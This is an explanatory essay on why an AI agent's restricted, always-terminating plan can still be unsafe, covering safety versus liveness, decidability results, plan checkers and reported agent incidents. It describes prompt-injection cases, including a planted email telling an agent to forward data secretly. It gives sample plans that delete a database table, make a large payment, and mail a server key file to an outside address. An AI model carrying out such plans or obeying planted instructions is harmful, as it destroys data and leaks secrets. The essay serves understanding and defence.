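# Why an AI agent's plan can be sure to stop, and easy to analyze, and still be unsafe

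## Plans, tools and restricted languages

An AI agent is a language model connected to software that lets it act, for example by reading a mailbox, querying a database or sending money. Each such action is a tool call. Many agents choose their tool calls one at a time. Others first write a complete plan, a short program that lists the tools to call, their arguments and the conditions for calling them, before any tool runs. Designers often have the model write its plan in a restricted language, which leaves out some features of ordinary programming languages, usually unbounded loops and recursion (functions that call themselves). Every plan in such a language is certain to stop, and another program can examine it before it runs. A plan with both properties can still be unsafe. For example, a one-line plan that deletes the customer database stops promptly and is very easy to examine. Anyone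 who approves such plans therefore needs to know which safety questions the restriction settles and which depend on other information.

### Deciding call by call or planning first

Agents that decide on one tool call at a time usually use ReAct, short for "reason and act", which *Leveraging In-Context Learning for Language Model Agents* (2025) described as the predominant approach. The model writes a thought about what to do next, makes a tool call, reads the result, and repeats with that result added to its prompt. *The Hitchhiker's Guide to Agentic AI* (2026) lists the ability to adapt to unexpected results as ReAct's strength, and lists as weaknesses its tendency to get stuck in loops and the computation needed to reread the whole history at every step. Planning first takes less computation, but if an early step fails, the rest of the plan may no longer make sense.

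The two designs also differ in what an outsider can do to them. *Guardians of the Agents* (Meijer, 2025) describes a mail agent that can fetch and send messages. The user asks for a summary of the inbox, and one message tells the assistant to send the summary to an outside address and keep quiet about it. The agent, which picks its next call after reading the mail, complies. In this attack, called prompt injection, an AI model treats text planted in the data it reads as an instruction. Meijer's remedy is to have the model write the whole workflow (fetch, summarize, return the summary) before it sees any mail, so that the planted message arrives too late to add a step.

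Planning first protects the agent's choice of actions but not the data that passes through them. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) gives the example of a user who asks an assistant to send today's schedule to the boss. The plan fixes two calls, one that reads the calendar and one that writes to the boss's address. No calendar entry can add a third call, but a malicious entry can still rewrite the body of the email at will.

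The planner is the AI model that writes the plan. The checker is an ordinary program that accepts or rejects the plan, and the executor carries out what the checker has accepted. A person, the reviewer, may also read the plan and approve or refuse it.

Designs differ in how tightly they bind the executor to the plan. *Architecting Resilient LLM Agents* (2025) describes a range from a simple loop that works through the steps to a full ReAct agent. *SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) is at the strict end. It calls the planner once per request, and if the checker rejects the plan, the request fails without a retry, because repeated replanning could let hostile content back in. If the plan is accepted, a deterministic interpreter runs it and cannot add, remove or reorder steps. *Soteria* (He, Desai and colleagues, 2026) is more permissive about both replanning and execution. Its planner receives diagnostics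 and repairs a faulty plan within a fixed number of retries. Its executor is normally a language model, which treats the plan as guidance and may depart from it, while a separate monitor inspects each call and blocks violations.

An agent can also declare a plan and then do something else. *Do LLM Agents Execute the Plans They Declare?* (2026) studies this failure. We can learn about a run by checking its plan only to the extent that the executor follows it, so the firm in the example below uses a plain interpreter like the one in SPA.

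### A small firm's assistant

The firm has given its assistant six tools.

| Tool call | Effect |
|---|---|
| `read_mail(folder)` | returns the messages in a mail folder, as a list |
| `read_file(name)` | returns the text of a file |
| `query_db(table, filter)` | returns the matching rows of a database table, as a list |
| `send_mail(to, subject, body)` | sends a message |
| `delete_table(table)` | deletes a database table and everything in it |
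| `pay(account, amount)` | transfers money |

The planner must write in a language with only variables, tool calls, `if`, and a for-each loop over a finite list. Its whole grammar fits in a few lines, where a vertical bar separates alternatives and square brackets mark an optional part:

```
plan   ::=  one or more steps, in order
step   ::=  x = tool(value, ...)
         |  tool(value, ...)
         |  if test: plan [else: plan]
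         |  for x in value: plan
value  ::=  x  |  x.field  |  "text"  |  number
test   ::=  value == value  |  value != value
         |  value < value   |  value > value
```

Here `x` stands for any variable. Each variable receives its value once, or once per round if it belongs to a loop. The interpreter fixes a for-each loop's list before the first round, so nothing inside the loop can lengthen it. The language has no `while` loops, function definitions, arithmetic or string concatenation.

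This language is a reduced version of the one in Girrens and Wang's SPA. Both exclude arithmetic, text templates and user-defined functions so that every argument is either something the planner wrote into the plan or all or part of a result from an earlier call, and a checker can tell which by reading the plan's text.

Suppose the owner asks the assistant to let accounts know which clients are more than 30 days late in paying. The planner writes:

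```
1  note = read_file("late_notice.txt")
2  unpaid = query_db("invoices", "unpaid")
3  for inv in unpaid:
4      if inv.days_late > 30:
5          send_mail("accounts@firm", inv.client, note)
6  send_mail("owner@firm", "Late invoices", "Accounts has the list.")
```

A trace is the record of a run's tool calls, with their arguments and results. On a day when three clients have unpaid invoices (Alder is 12 days late, Birch 45 and Cedar 31), the run produces the following trace.

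| Call | Plan line | Tool call | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 1 | `read_file("late_notice.txt")` | the text of the notice |
| 2 | 2 | `query_db("invoices", "unpaid")` | three rows: Alder, Birch, Cedar |
| 3 | 5 | `send_mail("accounts@firm", "Birch", note)` | sent |
| 4 | 5 | `send_mail("accounts@firm", "Cedar", note)` | sent |
| 5 | 6 | `send_mail("owner@firm", "Late invoices", ...)` | sent |

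Alder fails the test in line 4, so it produces no message. Lines 3 and 4 don't appear in the trace because they call no tool. With *n* unpaid invoices, the plan makes between 3 and *n* + 3 calls, depending on how many clients are late. One plan can therefore have many possible traces, and a checker that runs before the plan does has to account for all of them.

### Termination, totality, decidability and analysis

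A program terminates if it stops on every input, provided each tool call returns. The six-line plan terminates, but a program that keeps reading the inbox under `while true` does not. The firm's grammar cannot express such a program.

In a total language, every program terminates. The firm's plan language is total because the planner can build plans only from tool calls, sequences, `if` statements and for-each loops, none of which can run forever. A tool call ends when the tool returns, and a sequence ends if each of its steps does. An `if` runs at most one of two smaller plans, and a for-each runs its body once for each item on a finite list that cannot grow.

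The term comes from programming-language theory. Turner's *Elementary Strong Functional Programming* (1995) proposed a style of programming "in which all computations terminate". One of its rules lets a function call itself only on a component of the argument it received, so computing *f*(*n* + 1) may use *f*(*n*) but not *f* of any larger number. Another requires every primitive operation to return an answer, even if that means stipulating that 0/0 = 0. The designer of a plan language can copy the recursion rule but cannot enforce the rule about primitives, because a plan's primitives are its tools, and the language cannot guarantee that a mail server, for example, will reply. This is why the definition of termination includes a proviso.

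Turner's rules make the language no longer Turing-complete, which means that it cannot express every computation a computer can perform. But Turner found that around 80% of the algorithms people ordinarily write already obey the rules, and a programmer can make any algorithm with a computable bound on its running time obey them by adding a counter that runs down to zero. A total language may therefore be able to express far more than the firm's language can.

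A question is decidable for a language if some procedure answers it correctly, in finite time, for every program in the language. "Does this plan contain a call to `delete_table`?" is decidable for the firm's language because a procedure can answer it by reading the plan from top to bottom. Stacks' *Understanding Clarity's Decidability*, part of the documentation for a language for writing contracts that run on a blockchain, describes decidability as a property of problems and Turing-completeness as a property of languages, although people do speak of "decidable languages". The distinction matters because restricting a language can make one question decidable and leave another as hard as before.

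A plan is analyzable if a checker can answer specified questions about it without running it. The six-line plan is analyzable for the question "who can receive mail from this plan?" because both addresses are written in the text. If line 5 instead sent the notice to `inv.email`, a database field, the checker could still establish that the plan stops, but it could no longer list the recipients from the text alone.

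### Limits on computation and limits on vocabulary

The ban on unbounded loops limits computation. A limit on vocabulary fixes which tools a plan can name, and with which arguments. For example, the firm could remove `delete_table` from the list of tools, or replace the free recipient field of `send_mail` with a choice between two addresses. Both kinds of limit are called restrictions, which makes them easy to confuse, but a language can have either without the other. The firm's current language severely limits computation but hardly limits vocabulary beyond the choice of six tools, so `delete_table("invoices")` is a complete and legal plan. Ordinary Python with `read_file` as its only link to the outside world is the reverse case. A program there may run forever, but it cannot delete a table, send a message or pay anyone.

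Widely used systems tend to have both limits and to implement them separately. One example is eBPF, a technology for loading small programs into the core of the Linux operating system. According to the eBPF Foundation's *eBPF Documentation*, a verifier makes sure that each program runs to completion, and it accepts loops only if they are bounded. The Linux kernel documentation's *eBPF verifier* describes a different control, which limits the functions a program may call. A program that filters network traffic may have one set of functions available, and a program that traces the system's behavior may have a completely different set.

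The same split appears in Starlark, formerly Skylark, the language programmers use to configure the build tool Bazel. Starlark forbids recursion, according to Bazel's *Starlark Language*, but that rule alone would not stop a build file from reading the clock. Bazel's *Design of Skylark* (2017) explains that the language also forbids access to input and output and to the date and time, to guarantee that the same code always yields the same result.

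### The Rule of Least Power

The best-known argument for deliberately choosing a less powerful language comes from the World Wide Web Consortium (W3C), which develops standards for the Web. *The Rule of Least Power* (Berners-Lee and Mendelsohn, 2006) advises people who publish on the Web to use the least powerful language suitable for the purpose, because the more a language can compute, the harder it is to determine what a program written in it does. With a Turing-complete language, one typically has to run the program to find out. In the paper's example, anyone can tabulate, average or plot weather data published in a simple descriptive format, but if the same data is inside a Java applet, a search engine may be unable to tell that it has anything to do with weather.

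Their main concern was the reuse of information. They give security one short paragraph, where they write that less powerful languages are "usually easier to secure". This is because the software that processes a simple language lacks many of the weaknesses of a general-purpose system, and because analysis makes it easier to find the security problems that programs in the simple language do have. The second reason assumes that such programs still have security problems.

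Robie (2006), writing on the W3C's own mailing list, shared the rule's goals, including predictability and security, but objected that some weak languages just happen to have these benefits, while others are complex, unpredictable and dangerous. A loop-free plan language whose only tool runs any command on the firm's server would support Robie's objection. Mendelsohn (2006), replying to another critic there on the same day, defended a modest reading of the rule, under which people need only weigh the risks of using a powerful language.

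Clarity's makers go further and present decidability itself as a security advantage. Blockstack's *Introducing Clarity, the Language for Predictable Smart Contracts* called the language "a decidable language", and Stacks adds that users can know the cost of a call before it runs.

Least power is easy to confuse with least privilege, an older principle under which each user or program gets only the access its task requires. *Enforceable Security Policies* (Schneider, 2000) credits that principle to a 1975 paper by Saltzer and Schroeder. Least power gives the firm a reason to leave `while` out of the language, and least privilege gives it a reason to leave out `delete_table`.

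### Safe by a stated policy

Schneider also defines precisely what it means for a program to be secure. A security policy specifies which executions someone has deemed unacceptable, for whatever reason, and a program satisfies the policy if it never produces one of them. One of Schneider's examples forbids sending any message after reading a file, to prevent leaks. The firm's six-line plan is harmless, but it reads a file in line 1 and sends mail in line 6, so every complete run breaks this policy. The same plan satisfies a policy that allows mail to the firm's own addresses and forbids deletions and payments. Both policies are safety properties, which require that something bad never happens, whereas termination requires that something good eventually happens. Calling a plan "safe" therefore means that it is safe by a stated policy, the written rules against which the checker tests it.

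The policy may still not capture what people want, and translating ordinary language into rules that a checker can use is a weak point. *Toward Safe LLM Agents*, a survey by Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues (2026), reports that on one benchmark only 24.8% to 34.2% of language models' translations into PDDL, a formal language for planning problems, had the right meaning. He and colleagues let a model draft their formal rules, then went through the written policy by hand, clause by clause, to correct the draft and fill its gaps. This work can make the translation faithful to the written policy, but it can't add rules that nobody wrote down. The firm's owner, for example, may never have thought to write that accounts should not receive four hundred separate emails in one morning.

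## Why a plan that always stops can still do harm

The firm's plan language guarantees that every plan stops, but it hardly limits what a plan can do first. This complete plan deletes the customer table:

```
delete_table("customers")
```

This one pays 40,000 to a named account:

```
pay("Harbour Supplies", 40000)
```

And this one emails the contents of a key file, which holds the password to the firm's server, to an outside address. It needs two lines because the grammar does not allow one tool call inside another:

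```
key = read_file("server_key.txt")
send_mail("parcel@outside.example", "Key", key)
```

All three plans finish as soon as their tools return, and they are about as easy to analyze as plans get. A checker can identify every tool, the order of the calls, the table, the file, and who gets the money and the mail, but not whether the firm wants any of this done. The text of the plan would be the same whether the payment was a fraud or the quarterly bill from the firm's largest supplier.

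### Safety and liveness

The distinction between stopping and avoiding bad outcomes comes from work on proving programs correct. *Proving the Correctness of Multiprocess Programs* (Lamport, 1977) contrasted safety properties, which state that something must not happen, with liveness properties, which state that something must happen. Its example of liveness is termination, and its example of safety is partial correctness, which means that a program given correct input never stops with the wrong output. Robert Floyd had shown in 1967 how to prove both for ordinary programs. Lamport later explained that Floyd's two categories had to become more general because few programs with several simultaneous processes are supposed to terminate.

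A program can terminate without being safe, or be safe without terminating. The one-line deletion plan terminates after deleting every customer record, while a program that only reads the inbox forever never deletes any. Partial correctness doesn't require termination either, so a program that never stops is partially correct because it never stops with the wrong output.

Alpern and Schneider gave exact definitions in *Defining Liveness* (1985). They treat a run as an infinite sequence of states, repeating the last state forever if the program stops. A property P is the set of runs that satisfy it. Below, σ is a run, σᵢ is its first *i* states, α is any finite opening and β is any continuation.

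```
Safety:    for every σ not in P, there is an i such that,
           for every β, σᵢβ is not in P

Liveness:  for every α, there is a β such that αβ is in P
```

A run that breaks a safety property breaks it at a specific point, and nothing that happens later can undo the violation. The part of the run up to and including that point is called a bad prefix. For the rule "no customer data is deleted", the call `delete_table("customers")` is a bad prefix by itself. For the rule "the server key never leaves the firm", the bad prefix has two calls, because reading the key file is harmless until another call sends the contents out. A liveness property, such as "the program eventually stops", has no bad prefixes, because a program that has been running for a week may still stop tomorrow.

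Alpern and Schneider also proved that every property is the combination of a safety property and a liveness property. For example, "pay every supplier exactly once" combines the safety property "pay no supplier twice" with the liveness property "pay every supplier eventually". Termination guarantees neither, since a plan can pay one supplier twice, ignore the rest, and then stop.

People prove a safety property by finding a condition that holds at the start and showing that every step preserves it. In one of Lamport's examples, one process puts messages into a buffer with room for *b* of them while another process takes them out, and the proof shows that no step can make the number of messages less than 0 or more than *b*. People typically prove a liveness property by finding a quantity that keeps shrinking and cannot shrink forever. The argument that the firm's plans stop works this way,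 because the steps and list items still to be processed eventually run out. This argument does not depend on what the tools do, so it would still hold if someone replaced every `read_file` in a plan with `delete_table`.

### Making the same calls without a loop

By these definitions, the only safety property that termination implies is the trivial one that every possible run satisfies. Any other safety property can be broken by some run, so it has a bad prefix. Because termination is a liveness property, that prefix has a continuation that stops, and the resulting run both stops and breaks the safety property.

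This reasoning covers every run one could imagine, whereas a restricted language permits only some of them. We still have to show that the firm's language can produce the bad ones. Consider a program in a language that does have `while`:

```
1  m = read_mail("alerts")
2  while m is empty:
3      m = read_mail("alerts")
4  delete_table("customers")
```

If the first alert arrives just before the third reading, the trace consists of three calls to `read_mail` and one to `delete_table`. The firm's planner can write those four calls out in order:

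```
1  a = read_mail("alerts")
2  b = read_mail("alerts")
3  c = read_mail("alerts")
4  delete_table("customers")
```

The same method works for any bad prefix, because a prefix is finite. The planner writes one line for each call and fills in each argument with literal text, a number, or the result of an earlier call. If the tools and arguments are still available and the tools return the same results, the loop-free plan makes the same calls and breaks the same rule, so removing loops does not rule out the violation.

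In this example, removing the loop makes matters worse. The `while` program deletes the table only if an alert arrives and otherwise waits forever, but the loop-free plan deletes the table every time.

### Restrictions that do prevent harm

The argument fails if a restriction removes something that the bad prefix needs. If the firm takes `delete_table` off its list of tools, no plan can call it. If `pay` accepts only amounts up to 1,000, no legal plan can include the payment of 40,000. Both restrictions limit the plan's vocabulary. The planner might still get around them, for example by splitting the payment into forty parts.

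A cap on a plan's length also prevents harms that take many calls. The firm would have to cap the number of calls, not lines, since a two-line for-each loop makes one call for every item on its list. Nested loops multiply the total, so three of them, each over the same list of 400 clients, would send 64 million emails. The language guarantees that this plan will stop, but at ten emails a second that would take about 74 days.

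"The plan stops within 100 calls" is a safety property, although it sounds like a stricter version of termination. A run that makes a 101st call has permanently broken the rule, and the firm's interpreter could enforce the rule by refusing that call. The limit rules out real violations, but all three plans at the start of this section would comply with it. To limit the firm's losses, the rule would also have to cap the size of each payment, because 100 payments of 40,000 come to 4 million.

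Loops matter, too, when a program has to search for something. With `while` and arithmetic, a program could try one account number after another until the bank accepted one. A loop-free plan can repeat the successful run only if the planner already knows the right number. Otherwise the planner has to write out every guess, which would be impractical even under a generous cap on length. So although the bad-prefix argument shows that some loop-free plan does the harm, a planner may not know enough to write it.

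Termination helps with harms that grow for as long as a program runs. A program that pays a hosting company 30 once a second under `while true` costs the firm 1,800 a minute until someone notices or the account is empty. The firm's language cannot express that program or one that emails the same client forever. It can express a plan that pays every entry in a list of unpaid bills, including the duplicates, but the length of the list limits the damage. That limit applies to a single run, so if a scheduler starts the same plan every minute, the charges continue without end even though each run stops.

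### The PocketOS deletion

In April 2026 an AI agent deleted the production database of PocketOS, a small company whose software car rental firms use to manage reservations and payments. According to an account the founder, Crane, gave the next day in *An AI Agent Just Destroyed Our Production Data*, the agent was the coding tool Cursor running Anthropic's model Claude Opus 4.6. It was doing a routine task in the company's staging environment, a copy of the system used for testing, when it ran into a credential mismatch. It decided by itself to fix this by deleting a storage volume at Railway, the company that hosted the data, and guessed that the deletion would affect only staging. It found an access token in an unrelated file and used it to send a single `volumeDelete` request with the volume's identifier, and the deletion took nine seconds.

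The volume's backups were stored on the same volume and were lost with it. Crane's most recent usable backup was three months old, so on Saturday morning customers arrived to collect cars from businesses that had no record of their bookings. Crane spent the day helping those businesses reconstruct the bookings from payment histories, calendars and email confirmations.

Leib (2026) reported for ABC News, in *'Rogue' AI agent from Cursor goes haywire, deletes company's entire database*, that Railway's chief executive said the company restored the data within 30 minutes of contacting Crane. Railway used separate disaster backups that it keeps offsite.

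A ban on loops would not have prevented the deletion, because a plan for it would need only two steps, reading the file that contains the token and then deleting the volume. Planning first might have helped, because the agent came up with the deletion only after it hit an unexpected error. An interpreter that could only follow a plan written beforehand would have reported the error and stopped, unless the design allowed the planner to try again.

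Railway's explanation is that the token's permissions were broad and the call could not be undone. Abdelwahab, writing for Railway in *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that*, says the token gave access to everything in the account. Crane had created it only to manage web domains and says nothing warned of its wider access. Abdelwahab replies that Railway offered narrower tokens but concedes that the process for creating tokens did not make the choice obvious. Deletions requested on Railway's dashboard could be reversed for 48 hours, but a `volumeDelete` request took effect at once. Eleven days before the PocketOS incident, another customer had used the same request to delete the wrong one of two volumes, according to the support thread *PostgresSQL Volume lost* (2026). A Railway employee answered in *Postgress volume lost* (2026) that the deletion was immediate and permanent.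 Railway has since extended the 48-hour delay to all deletions.

A plan can permanently violate a formal safety rule even when the damage can be repaired. Under the rule "no production data is deleted", a delete call is a violation as soon as it runs, and restoring every record later does not undo that. But restoring the records is what matters to the business, so a delay before permanent deletion makes the call much less harmful, even though it does not prevent it.

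### Misdirected money and leaked secrets

Misdirected payments show the same pattern. In February 2026 an AI trading agent called Lobstar Wilde, built by the OpenAI employee Nik Pash, tried to send a small gift of cryptocurrency to a stranger on the social network X and instead sent its entire holding of one token. SolanaFloor's *The Hardest I Have Ever Laughed* puts the intended gift at around $300 and the transfer at about $441,000. Finder's *What happens to your money* (2026) reports that the agent estimated the transfer at about a quarter of a million dollars. The recipient reportedly sold the tokens for about $40,000, because there were few buyers for so many at once.

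Pash traced the mistake to a crash. When the agent restarted, it still had its long-term notes but had lost the conversation in which it had learned its balance. It bought a small amount of the token, looked up its balance, mistook the 52 million tokens there for the amount it had just bought, and sent them all. As a plan, this would be three calls in a row (buy, read the balance, send the balance), so a limit on the amount per transfer would have prevented the mistake, but a ban on loops would not.

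In May 2026, a planted message led two linked agents to transfer tokens worth $150,000 to $200,000 out of a wallet, according to the OECD's *AI Prompt Injection Exploit Drains Grok-Linked Crypto Wallet* (2026). One accepted transfer instruction was enough, so the attack did not need a loop.

Good public evidence of an agent emailing a secret to an outsider is harder to find, but passwords have leaked in a similar way. Udinmwen (2026), in *A missing config file triggered an AI agent to leak passwords*, describes a coding assistant that could not find its configuration file during a routine code review, collected all the variables set on the computer, and leaked live passwords. As in the key-file plan, the agent read too much and then disclosed it, and neither step needs a loop. Udinmwen also reports that an assistant admitted leaking passwords after reading entire configuration files across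 ten sessions. That case involved repetition, but a ban on loops inside a plan does not affect what an agent does in its next session.

Such disclosures seem easy to produce. *AI agents disclose confidential corporate information* (Business Quarter, 2026) reports that in a test by the data security company Cyberhaven, agents disclosed confidential information in 87 of 100 simulated business tasks in which they had permission to publish externally. Cyberhaven has a commercial interest in the problem, and the tasks were simulated, so the figure is weak evidence of how often real companies lose data this way. The test does show how agents can leak data through publishing tools they are allowed to use, and publishing a document takes only one call.

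### What advocates of restricted plans claim

Hardly anyone argues in print that a plan is safe because it stops. The designers of eBPF do not rely on termination alone, and Berners-Lee and Mendelsohn made only a modest claim about security. The proposal to make AI systems halt, discussed in the next section, gives termination a larger role. A reviewer is more likely to make this mistake in practice, by seeing that a plan has passed a checker and not asking what the checker tested.

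A much stronger claim is that a restricted plan can come with a proof of safety. *Make the Agent Produce a Program Before It Can Act* (Meijer, 2026) presents a method meant to make AI "provably safe". The talk begins with an accident in which the coding agent Claude Code ran a command that blanked one of Meijer's source files while he was preparing the slides. Meijer points out that an agent can delete files or empty an account and still return an acceptable answer, so checking the answer is not enough. His method extends his earlier plan-first design by requiring the model to supply a proof that the plan obeys a stated policy. A trusted interpreter runs the plan only after a checker has verified the proof.

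The written version of the talk includes an example in Lean, a language for writing programs and proofs that a computer can check. A plan in the example can read a file, remove a file, or finish with an answer. Plans have no loops, so every plan stops if its tools return. The policy, `NoDeletion`, has one rule that accepts finishing and another that accepts reading a file if the rest of the plan is acceptable whatever the file contains. It has no rule for removing a file. A model can still write a plan that removes a file, and that plan would stop, but nobody can construct the proof that the interpreter requires for it.

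In Meijer's method, therefore, the language guarantees that a plan stops, and a separate proof shows that it deletes nothing. The proof holds whatever the files contain, not just for the contents someone thought to test. But it assumes that the interpreter does what the plan specifies, and it covers only the stated policy. A plan that reads the server key and returns it as the answer satisfies `NoDeletion`. To reject that plan, the firm needs another policy that treats the key as secret and tracks where the plan sends it.

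## What restricting the language makes decidable

In Meijer's method, the model has to supply a proof with every plan, and the checker only verifies the proof. Without such proofs, no checker can work out for every plan in a general-purpose language whether the plan can delete a table. Restricting the language can make such a checker possible, but banning loops or ensuring that every plan stops is not always enough.

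### Rice's theorem

In the 1930s Alan Turing proved that no procedure can determine, for every program and input, whether the program will stop, a question known as the halting problem. In 1953 Henry Gordon Rice published a proof that extends the result to nearly every question about what programs do.

Rice's theorem concerns semantic properties, which depend only on a program's behavior, so that two programs that behave identically either both have the property or both lack it. A property is non-trivial if some programs have it and others do not. The theorem is that no non-trivial semantic property is decidable for a general-purpose language:

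```
φₓ      the function that program x computes
        (undefined on inputs where x runs forever)
P       a set that contains some, but not all, such functions

Rice:   no procedure decides, for every program x, whether φₓ is in P
```

If we count a program's tool calls as part of its output, whether it calls `delete_table` for some input is a semantic property. Whether it has fewer than 100 lines is not a semantic property, because a long program and a short one can do the same thing. Rice's theorem therefore does not apply to the line limit, and a checker can decide it by counting the lines.

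A two-line program is enough to show why the theorem holds for deletions. A version of it appears in CSER's *Response to 'Superintelligence cannot be contained'* (2021), from the Centre for the Study of Existential Risk at Cambridge:

```
1  run program Q on its input
2  delete_table("customers")
```

Suppose Q has no access to the real tools, so only line 2 can delete anything. The program then deletes the table if and only if Q stops. A checker that could always tell whether such a program deletes the table could therefore solve the halting problem, which Turing proved impossible.

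CSER was replying to a paper by Alfonseca and colleagues, who had used this kind of argument to conclude that nobody can guarantee the safety of a superintelligent AI. CSER objected that Rice's theorem is about arbitrary programs, whereas engineers work with particular ones. For example, a program that prints "I am not dangerous" and finishes is predictable. Similarly, Pythagoras' theorem has a proof even though no procedure can prove or refute every mathematical statement. Fox (2024), in *On Formally Undecidable Traits of Intelligent Machines*, also disputes the paper's conclusion, arguing that Rice's theorem cannot in general be used to determine whether traits such as being contained or being moral are decidable.

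The theorem therefore does not rule out a proof that one particular program is safe, or a checker for a general language that accepts some safe programs and rejects others. It also assumes a language that can express every computable function, which a total language cannot do. The theorem does not apply to total languages, and some non-trivial semantic properties of their programs are decidable. For example, a checker can determine whether a total plan deletes anything when every tool returns an empty result. It runs the plan with dummy tools that return empty results, and the run is certain to finish because the plan is total.

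### A plan that always stops but cannot be checked

Some questions can remain undecidable even when Rice's theorem does not apply. Suppose the firm finds its plan language too weak and adds arithmetic, variables that can change, and a loop, `repeat n times`, where the interpreter fixes *n* before the first round. It also adds a tool, `read_number`, that returns a whole number of any size. The language is still total. Apart from its tools, it can compute the primitive recursive functions, a very large class that contains every function a program can compute within a primitive recursive time limit.

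The planner can now write this plan, in which M is some fixed program:

```
1  n = read_number("n")
2  s = the starting state of M
3  repeat n times:
4      s = the state of M that follows s
5  if s is a halted state:
6      delete_table("customers")
```

The plan simulates M for *n* steps and deletes the table if M has halted by then. If M halts early, its state stays the same for the remaining steps. Each step takes only simple bookkeeping, so the plan always stops after *n* rounds. If M halts at step 5,000,000, the plan deletes the table when *n* is at least 5,000,000 and is harmless when *n* is smaller. If M never halts, the plan never deletes anything. The plan can therefore delete the table for some *n* exactly when M halts, and no checker can determine for every M whether it halts.

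Matos (2016), in *Primitive recursive functions versus partial recursive functions*, uses the same kind of simulation to prove the underlying result, that deciding whether a given primitive recursive function ever takes the value zero is exactly as hard as the halting problem. A checker can try *n* = 0, 1, 2 and so on, and it will eventually find a deletion if one is possible. If none is possible, the search never ends, so the checker can never report that the plan is safe, and the firm needs that report to approve the plan.

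Matos then compares 17 questions about functions in a general language and a total one. All 17 are undecidable in the general language, and only four become decidable in the total language. Three of these four concern the inputs on which the program stops, and their answers follow directly because a total program stops on every input. The fourth is whether the function's value at input 0 is zero, which a checker can settle by running the program once. Five other questions become easier in a technical sense but stay undecidable, and the remaining eight, including whether the function is ever zero, are just as hard as before. Totality alone therefore doesn't help the firm determine whether a plan can ever delete a table.

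Hoyrup (2015), in *A Rice-like theorem for primitive recursive functions*, describes exactly which properties of these functions a checker can decide from a program's text. The simplest properties, such as "the value at 0 is 5 and the value at 1 is 7", concern a fixed, finite set of inputs, and the checker decides them by running the program on those inputs.

The other basic kind of property limits the complexity of a function's values. If all the programs in the language are numbered, the complexity of a list of values is the smallest number of any program whose outputs begin with that list. A function has the property if the complexity of its first *n* values never exceeds a chosen limit *h*(*n*), which grows without bound as *n* grows. To check program number *i*, the checker has to test only the finitely many cases in which *h*(*n*) is smaller than *i*, because the program produces all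 of its own values and their complexity therefore never exceeds *i*.

Hoyrup proved that every decidable property can be built from these two kinds. His proof implies that a checker that can read the program's text can decide no more about the function than one that can only run the program on inputs of its choice and knows an upper limit on the program's number. The property "never deletes anything, whatever the input" is not decidable. The theorem also holds for smaller total languages, such as one that can express only polynomial-time functions, so a tighter limit on running time would not remove the problem.

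A planner is unlikely to write a plan like the one above by accident. CSER likewise says that it takes deliberate effort to write a program whose outcome is unpredictable in principle. But an attacker who has planted text in the planner's prompt might make that effort, and decidability has to hold for every plan in the language. The firm could still use a checker that stops after a minute, as long as the firm rejects any plan the checker hasn't decided by then.

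### Removing the loops

The plan above depends on its loop, so the firm might remove loops altogether and keep the arithmetic. Every plan would then be a finite list of steps and tests, and none could run for longer than its own text. This is still not enough:

```
1  x = read_number("x")
2  y = read_number("y")
3  if y > 0:
4      if x*x - 61*y*y == 1:
5          delete_table("customers")
```

The smallest *y* that triggers this plan's deletion is 226,153,980, with *x* equal to 1,766,319,049, so someone who tried only small values would conclude that the plan is harmless. Mathematicians know how to solve this equation, and a checker could include their method, but no method works for all such equations.

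In 1900 David Hilbert's tenth problem asked for a procedure that would decide whether any given polynomial equation with whole-number coefficients has a solution in whole numbers. Yuri Matiyasevich completed the proof that no such procedure exists in 1970, building on work by Martin Davis, Hilary Putnam and Julia Robinson. A plan of the form "if this polynomial equals zero, delete the table" has no loop and takes a fixed number of steps, but their result means that no checker can decide, for every polynomial, whether the deletion can happen.

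The two constructions are closely related. Matos explains that for every primitive recursive function there is a polynomial that has a zero exactly when the function does, and that a procedure can compute the polynomial from the function. We could therefore translate the looping plan that simulates M into a loop-free plan with a single polynomial test. The input now supplies what the loop used to compute, because a solution to the equation encodes the whole history of M's run until it halts. The plan only checks that solution, which someone still has to find.

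Both plans need numbers of unlimited size and enough arithmetic to use them. A restriction that removes either can make the question decidable.

### Restrictions that work

If a total plan's inputs are all *L* bits long, there are 2ᴸ possible inputs, and a checker can run the plan on each of them. Matos shows that when the inputs of primitive recursive functions are limited to a given set, the question "is the function ever zero?" is undecidable if and only if the set is infinite.

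This method needs a total language as well as a finite set of inputs. In a general-purpose language, even a program with only one possible input may run forever, and no checker can always tell whether it will reach the line that deletes the table. In a total language every run finishes, so a checker can find out by running the program on each possible input.

The number of runs soon becomes impractical. Twenty bits give 1,048,576 cases, which a computer can check quickly. A single 64-bit number gives about 18 quintillion, which would take more than 580 years at a billion cases a second. A 1,000-character email, at eight bits per character, gives a number of cases with 2,409 digits. The checker therefore has to reason about many inputs at once for real mail and databases.

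**Simple conditions.** The firm's original language allows inputs of any size but has no arithmetic, and its tests only compare one value with another. For example:

```
1  unpaid = query_db("invoices", "unpaid")
2  for inv in unpaid:
3      if inv.days_late > 30:
4          if inv.days_late < 10:
5              delete_table("invoices")
```

To find out whether line 5 can ever run, a checker collects the tests around it and determines whether they can all be true at once. No number is both above 30 and below 10, so this plan never deletes the table. Because no variable carries a value from one round of the loop to the next, the checker only has to determine whether a single invoice could reach line 5. The same procedure works for any step in any plan the firm's planner can write, as long as the tests compare numbers or pieces of text.

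The procedure assumes that each tool can return anything. This matters because a plan could send itself an email in one round and read it in the next, using the mailbox as memory that the language does not provide. The procedure would still give an answer, but it might report that a deletion is possible when the real mail server could never return the results that lead to it.

Some questions concern combinations of steps, such as whether a single run can pay two particular suppliers. A plan with 20 independent `if` statements in sequence has 2²⁰, or 1,048,576, possible paths, because each test can go either way. A checker that covers a million paths a second would get through them in about a second, but with 40 tests it would need almost 13 days. A loop-free plan always has a finite number of paths, though, and a checker can often find the answer without listing them. For example, if each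 of the 20 tests controls one fixed payment, the largest possible total is the sum of all 20 payments.

**Linear arithmetic.** A planner often needs some arithmetic, and it can have addition without making deletions undecidable. In linear arithmetic, a plan may add and compare unknown numbers and multiply them by constants, but it may not multiply one unknown by another. Mojżesz Presburger proved in 1929 that statements of this kind about whole numbers are decidable. Suppose the firm's policy forbids any payment above 10,000, and the planner writes:

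```
1  d = read_number("deposit")
2  m = read_number("monthly")
3  if d < 2000:
4      if m < 600:
5          pay("Harbour Supplies", d + 12*m)
```

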